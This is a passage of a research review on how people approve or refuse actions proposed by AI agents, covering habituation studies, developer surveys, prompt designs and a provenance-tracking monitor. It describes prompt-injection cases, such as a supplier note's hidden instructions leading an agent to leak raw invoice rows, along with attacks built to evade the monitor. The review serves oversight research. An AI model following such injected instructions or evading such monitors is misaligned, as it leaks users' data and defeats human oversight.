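Anthropic measured the unsafe approval rate in an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, who did coding tasks in a test environment. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command. The testers knew they were in an evaluation, but not that it concerned their answers to prompts. Approving the command did nothing harmful.

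Testers blocked only 143 of the 1,053 dangerous commands, so the unsafe approval rate was 86.4%. Auto mode's classifier blocked 937 of the same commands. Testers blocked about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The habituation experiments with installation dialogs showed a similar decline.

The testers had no code or data of their own at risk, and people may be more careful with their own projects. Anthropic published the study to support its decision to make auto mode the default. Its article gives no examples of the commands. The experiment measured how bad the problem is with ordinary prompts, but it did not vary the prompt's design, so it does not show how much highlighting a host or path would reduce the problem.

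### What developers say they check

Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, asked 203 developers how often they approve seven types of agent action without close review. 36% said they often do so for access to the internet, external services or connected tools, and 21% said the same for reading secrets and other sensitive files, the lowest share of the seven types. 64% said they often do so for at least one type.

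Developers therefore seem to check more carefully when an agent reads a secret than when it contacts a website, although an agent has to do both to leak a password over the internet. The outgoing request is the last chance to stop the leak. Action A fetches a web page, the type of action that developers check least.

Developers who reviewed code carefully were not reliably more careful when approving actions. Among those who thoroughly reviewed most or all of the agent's code, 61% often approved some type of action without close review, compared with 67% of the others, a difference that could easily be due to chance. However, developers who inspected diffs, which show the changed lines of a file, were less likely to approve requests to read secrets or run destructive commands without close review. Wu, Wermke and colleagues suggest that a diff gives people something concrete to check. That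 would be a reason to show the new lines in the prompt for action B, but careful people may simply be more likely to read diffs.

Of the developers who knew of a security or privacy incident or a worrying practice involving agents, 70% often approved at least one type of action without close review, compared with 43% of those who knew of none. Heavy users probably hear about more incidents and also see more prompts, but the difference remained after the researchers adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents. The survey cannot show whether the awareness or the approval habit came first, and only 46 people knew of no incidents.

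People reported these habits themselves. Approving a familiar action without close review can also be reasonable. The researchers discarded 380 of 583 submissions, many of which were duplicates or suspiciously fast.

In a second study, *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) asked software practitioners what they look at when they read a prompt. They interviewed 18 people and then surveyed 115 others, 107 of whom answered the questions about permissions. Of those 107, 47.7% said they read requests carefully, 33.6% said they skim and 20.6% said they approve by default. Only 31.8% said they check the file that a request names, and 25.2% said they focus on the command or title. If these answers are accurate, most people don't make a point of checking the details that a client would highlight. Highlighting might draw their attention to the file, or they might ignore the highlighting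 because they don't think the file matters.

About three-quarters of respondents looked more closely at requests to write, delete or gain higher privileges, and 63.6% did so when a request was unexpected. Nearly all (98.1%) were more willing to grant read-only access. That willingness is risky because a read can be the first step in a leak, and action A also looks read-only if the prompt describes it as fetching a page.

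In the same survey, 61.7% of respondents said they would never grant an agent access to sensitive data. To follow that rule, they would have to recognise the data in a prompt, which is difficult for people who skim. A third of respondents admitted they had become less careful over time. One interviewee had worried about permissions at first but stopped caring after seeing many similar requests.

When asked what they wanted, 45.8% of respondents chose a clearer view of what the agent had accessed. One interviewee imagined a map of the file system showing everywhere the agent had been. Another refused several requests, then watched the agent continue without asking, and could not tell whether it had complied with the refusals or found a way around them.

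### Four versions of an approval prompt

No published experiment appears to have compared an agent's approval prompt with and without highlighting. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, came closest by testing four prompts that showed increasing amounts of information. They recruited 80 volunteers through social media and assigned 20 to each version. Every participant judged 12 requests about email, shared documents or purchasing, and six of the 12 broke the user's instructions. This produced 960 decisions in total:

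| Version | What it showed | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Comprehension score | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | A brief account of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 57.1% | 16.3 s |
| Exact arguments | The same, plus the tool's arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 67.9% | 23.4 s |
| Full log | The same, plus the user's instructions and all earlier events in time order | 32.5% | 87.5% | 76.7% | 38.6 s |
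| Linked summary | The facts in the full log, organised around the combined effect of the action and the earlier steps | 24.2% | 85.8% | 81.7% | 33.2 s |

The step from a short description to the exact arguments matters most for hosts and paths, because the arguments contain them. Unsafe approvals fell from 66 of 120 to 52 of 120, a drop of 11.7 percentage points. A rough 95% margin of error for a difference between two shares is:

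1.96 × √(p₁(1 − p₁)/n + p₂(1 − p₂)/n)

With p₁ = 0.550, p₂ = 0.433 and n = 120, the margin is 12.6 points, so the true effect could be anywhere from a rise of about 1 point to a drop of 24. This range is too narrow because the formula treats all 120 decisions as independent, when each participant made six of them. If each person's answers were correlated at 0.2, the margin would grow to about 18 points.

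Comparing the first version with the last gives stronger evidence that more information helps. The drop between them is 30.8 points, with a rough margin of 11.7, so it would probably remain after accounting for repeated answers.

The second version made visible arguments that the first had not shown, so the result is evidence about clients that hide the host. It does not show whether a client that already displays the host should print it in bold. The linked summary highlighted the log entries that supported it, but it also rearranged the rest of the screen, so the experiment cannot isolate the effect of the highlighting.

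Showing more information also had drawbacks. People took about twice as long with the linked summary as with the short description. At the median times, 30 prompts would take 17 minutes instead of 8. They also rated the work as more demanding and approved slightly fewer legitimate requests.

The linked summary and the full log contained the same facts, but the summary did better on most measures. After adjustment, the unsafe approval rate was 7.9 percentage points lower with the summary, but the 95% interval ran from 19.7 points lower to 3.8 points higher. Hossain and colleagues call their analysis exploratory because they did not preregister it.

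All four unsafe approval rates were far below the 86.4% in Anthropic's experiment, but the commands, the people and the situation all differed. The volunteers only judged requests, half of which were harmful. Anthropic's testers were trying to finish a coding task and met one dangerous command among many ordinary ones, which is closer to how developers normally work.

### Violations that depend on earlier steps

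Hossain and colleagues distinguish two kinds of violation. A local violation is visible in the proposed action itself, such as sending a file to someone the user has ruled out. A cumulative violation is visible only when a reviewer connects the action with earlier steps.

In the main example, a user asks an agent to check supplier invoices and send only the summary totals to an outside auditor. A supplier's note contains hidden instructions, and the agent copies the raw invoice rows into `report.csv`, then asks to send the file to the auditor. The user has approved the auditor as a recipient, and the file name is unremarkable, but the file contains data the user wanted to withhold.

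Highlighting the recipient cannot reveal this problem, because the recipient is correct. The highlight might even reassure the user. The same could happen to the developer with the failing build. Suppose the agent copies part of the error log into `build-notes.txt` and later asks to upload that file to `docs.example.org`, which is on the allowlist. The prompt would show a trusted host and a harmless file name, but the uploaded file would contain Ana's email address.

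Hossain and colleagues write that highlighting the destination is enough for local violations, but they did not test this, and their results give some reason to doubt it. People shown the full log, including the exact recipient and the user's instructions, still approved 10 of 40 local violations. With the linked summary, they approved 7 of 40.

To produce the summary, the system tracks where each file came from:

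1. A recorder that the agent cannot alter logs each tool call, with its real arguments and effects.
2. When the agent creates a file from other files, the new file inherits the origins of all of them.
3. Before an important action, a monitor works out the combined effect. In the example, the agent would send the auditor a file that has raw invoice rows among its origins.
4. The monitor compares this effect with the user's instructions and returns one of three results: allowed, violation or unknown. "Unknown" means that the record is incomplete.
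5. The prompt quotes the user's instructions, states the combined effect just above the buttons and links to the events behind it. It leaves the reviewer to decide whether the effect breaks the instructions.

Step 2 can be written as a rule about sets:

origins(new file) ⊇ origins(input 1) ∪ … ∪ origins(input k)

The new file's origins include every origin of its inputs. If an agent makes a file from a public template and a customer's record, the file counts as derived from both, even if the agent copied nothing from the record. This rule stops the system from losing track of private data, but it can also make a harmless file look sensitive. Lan and colleagues proposed similar labels for content from web pages.

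The researchers tested the monitor separately, without human reviewers, on 120 violations and 120 matching harmless cases. It detected 107 of the violations, missed seven and returned "unknown" for six. It also raised five false alerts. They then removed parts of the system or made its task harder:

| Version of the test | Cumulative violations detected, out of 80 | False alerts, out of 120 |
|---|---|---|
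| Complete monitor | 69 | 5 |
| No links between a file and its sources | 48 | 6 |
| No accumulated record of earlier steps | 16 | 3 |
| No comparison with the user's instructions | 30 | 15 |
| Some events missing from the record | 51 | 8 |
| Attacks designed to evade the monitor | 60 | 5 |

The fourth row is relevant to lists of sensitive hosts and paths. Without the user's own instructions, the monitor could only judge whether an action looked sensitive in general, and it missed most cumulative violations and raised three times as many false alerts.

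The monitor can also block an action instead of informing a person. In 240 test runs with malicious content, two small open models carried out a forbidden action 110 times when every request was approved automatically. When the monitor blocked violations and unknown cases, they did so 13 times. The number of ordinary tasks they completed fell from 214 to 206 out of 240. It fell further when some events were missing from the record, because the monitor blocked many actions it could not assess.

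In the balanced test, about 95% of the monitor's alerts were correct. The share would be much lower in real use, where harmful requests are rare.

People may not understand a violation even when the summary describes it correctly. When a violation depended on a chain of several steps, participants approved seven of 30 with the linked summary and seven of 30 with the log. Hossain and colleagues think one sentence may be too short for such cases, and suggest a small diagram or a step-by-step explanation. They also warn that people might trust a confident summary that is wrong, but they have not yet tested this.

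### Requests for data the agent does not need

To judge action A, the developer has to realise that the lookup would work without Ana's email address. Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025) tested a similar judgement in *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*. They recruited 205 people to train an imaginary personal assistant, which asked to share particular pieces of their data with tools such as a travel-booking service. Each person answered 20 permission questions, five of which included data that the task did not need.

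The researchers gave people every reason to be careful. They asked about privacy concerns at the start, and each permission question included a warning that the assistant or its tools might collect unnecessary data. Participants also indicated which data they thought a task required. The table shows how often they agreed to share, either once or always:

| | Participant thought the task needed the data | Participant thought it did not |
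|---|---|---|
| The task needed the data | 89% | 67% |
| The task did not need the data | 78% | 38% |

People shared unnecessary data about twice as often when they mistakenly thought the task needed it. The prompts named the data, so participants had more trouble judging whether a request was justified than seeing which data the assistant requested. For action A, a line such as "the error code alone is enough for this search" might help more than bolding the email address. It might not be enough, though, since people still shared 38% of the data they correctly considered unnecessary.

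The type of data also mattered. Participants withheld their US Social Security numbers in 46% of cases, even when a task required them. They shared details that seemed harmless much more freely, and unnecessarily gave the name of a workspace in the chat app Slack in 89% of cases.

No data left anyone's computer in this study, so participants' choices had no consequences. Participants were also deciding about their own data, whereas the developer in action A is deciding about Ana's. The developer may guard her data less closely than their own, or more closely if an employer has strict rules.

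Wu, Yang and colleagues also built a model that predicted people's answers with 85.1% accuracy, as a step towards an assistant that would grant permissions for them. The score measures agreement with people's choices, so an assistant could reach it while repeating their mistakes. Salerno and colleagues warn against treating repeated approvals as a preference, because they may only reflect fatigue or a deadline.

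### Rules that people write in advance

If people make poor decisions in the middle of a task, they might do better by setting rules beforehand. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) tested this with 113 people who did not work in software. They supervised an agent through a simulated day of email, travel and errands. Eleven of the agent's 18 actions were necessary for the tasks, and the other seven went beyond them, such as reading private messages or buying travel insurance.

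The first group approved or refused every action. In the second group, a model allowed some actions and referred the rest to the person. The third group started by choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting something and reading private information.

| Who decided | Unrequested actions blocked | Unrequested actions approved when a prompt appeared |
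|---|---|---|
| The person, every time | 60% | 40% |
| A model first, then the person | 54% | 46% |
| The person's own rules, then the person | 40% | 67% |

The group that set its own rules had the weakest protection. People chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which postponed the decision until the agent was about to act, and then they usually said yes. Of the 148 unrequested actions that went ahead in this group, people had approved 133 when asked, and the other 15 ran automatically under an "allow" rule.

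The last column needs care because people in the third group saw a prompt only if they had chosen "ask" for that category. Those who chose "ask" may have differed from those who chose "never", and Yan's results cannot show why they approved more.

Every prompt described the action in plain language and named the data, recipient or amount involved. People still approved at least 40% of the unrequested actions, and most participants let some through. Their decisions depended on the action. In the group that decided every time, 88% allowed an unnecessary call to the airport to confirm a flight, but only 21% let the agent post publicly that they were travelling. Some approvals may have been sensible, since a person can welcome an action they did not request.

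Other approvals contradicted what the same people had said earlier. Before the simulation, participants had judged examples of actions as ones the agent should do automatically, ask about first or never do. In the group with its own rules, participants approved 24 of the 56 prompts for actions they had said the agent should never take.

Yan's second group also offers a small test of whether people become more suspicious when prompts are rarer and more often justified. The model referred ten actions to each person in this group, and seven of them went beyond the task, compared with seven of 18 in the first group. The second group approved actions that went beyond the task no less often than the first, perhaps because nothing told them that most of the harmless requests had already gone through. A client that filters requests this way could say so in the prompt.

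Participants reported a strong sense of control in all three groups, so their satisfaction was a poor guide to how well each design protected them.

### When extra information reassures people

Confidence can also mislead people who review an agent's finished work. *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (2026) describes three user studies in which people missed errors in the usual list of an agent's steps. The researchers then tested a new display that helped people move between the task's requirements and the steps, but it made people more confident, especially when they were wrong.

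Li, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *Are You Sure?*, gave 303 participants realistic tasks to do with an agent, such as choosing a job candidate or managing a mailbox. They secretly manipulated what the agent read, remembered or did so that it worked against the participants. Only 8.6% of participants noticed that something was wrong. Technical experts did worse in some scenarios because they trusted the agent's process and gave less attention to its output.

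Security warnings often increased people's trust in the agent, apparently because the warnings made the agent seem open about its risks. A label in an approval prompt could have the same effect if developers take it as a sign that the client has the risks under control.

Li and colleagues recommend warnings that interrupt the task and are quick to verify. The redrawn prompt for action A already names `ana@example.com` and its source. A link to the exact line of the error log would let the developer check the warning in a few seconds.
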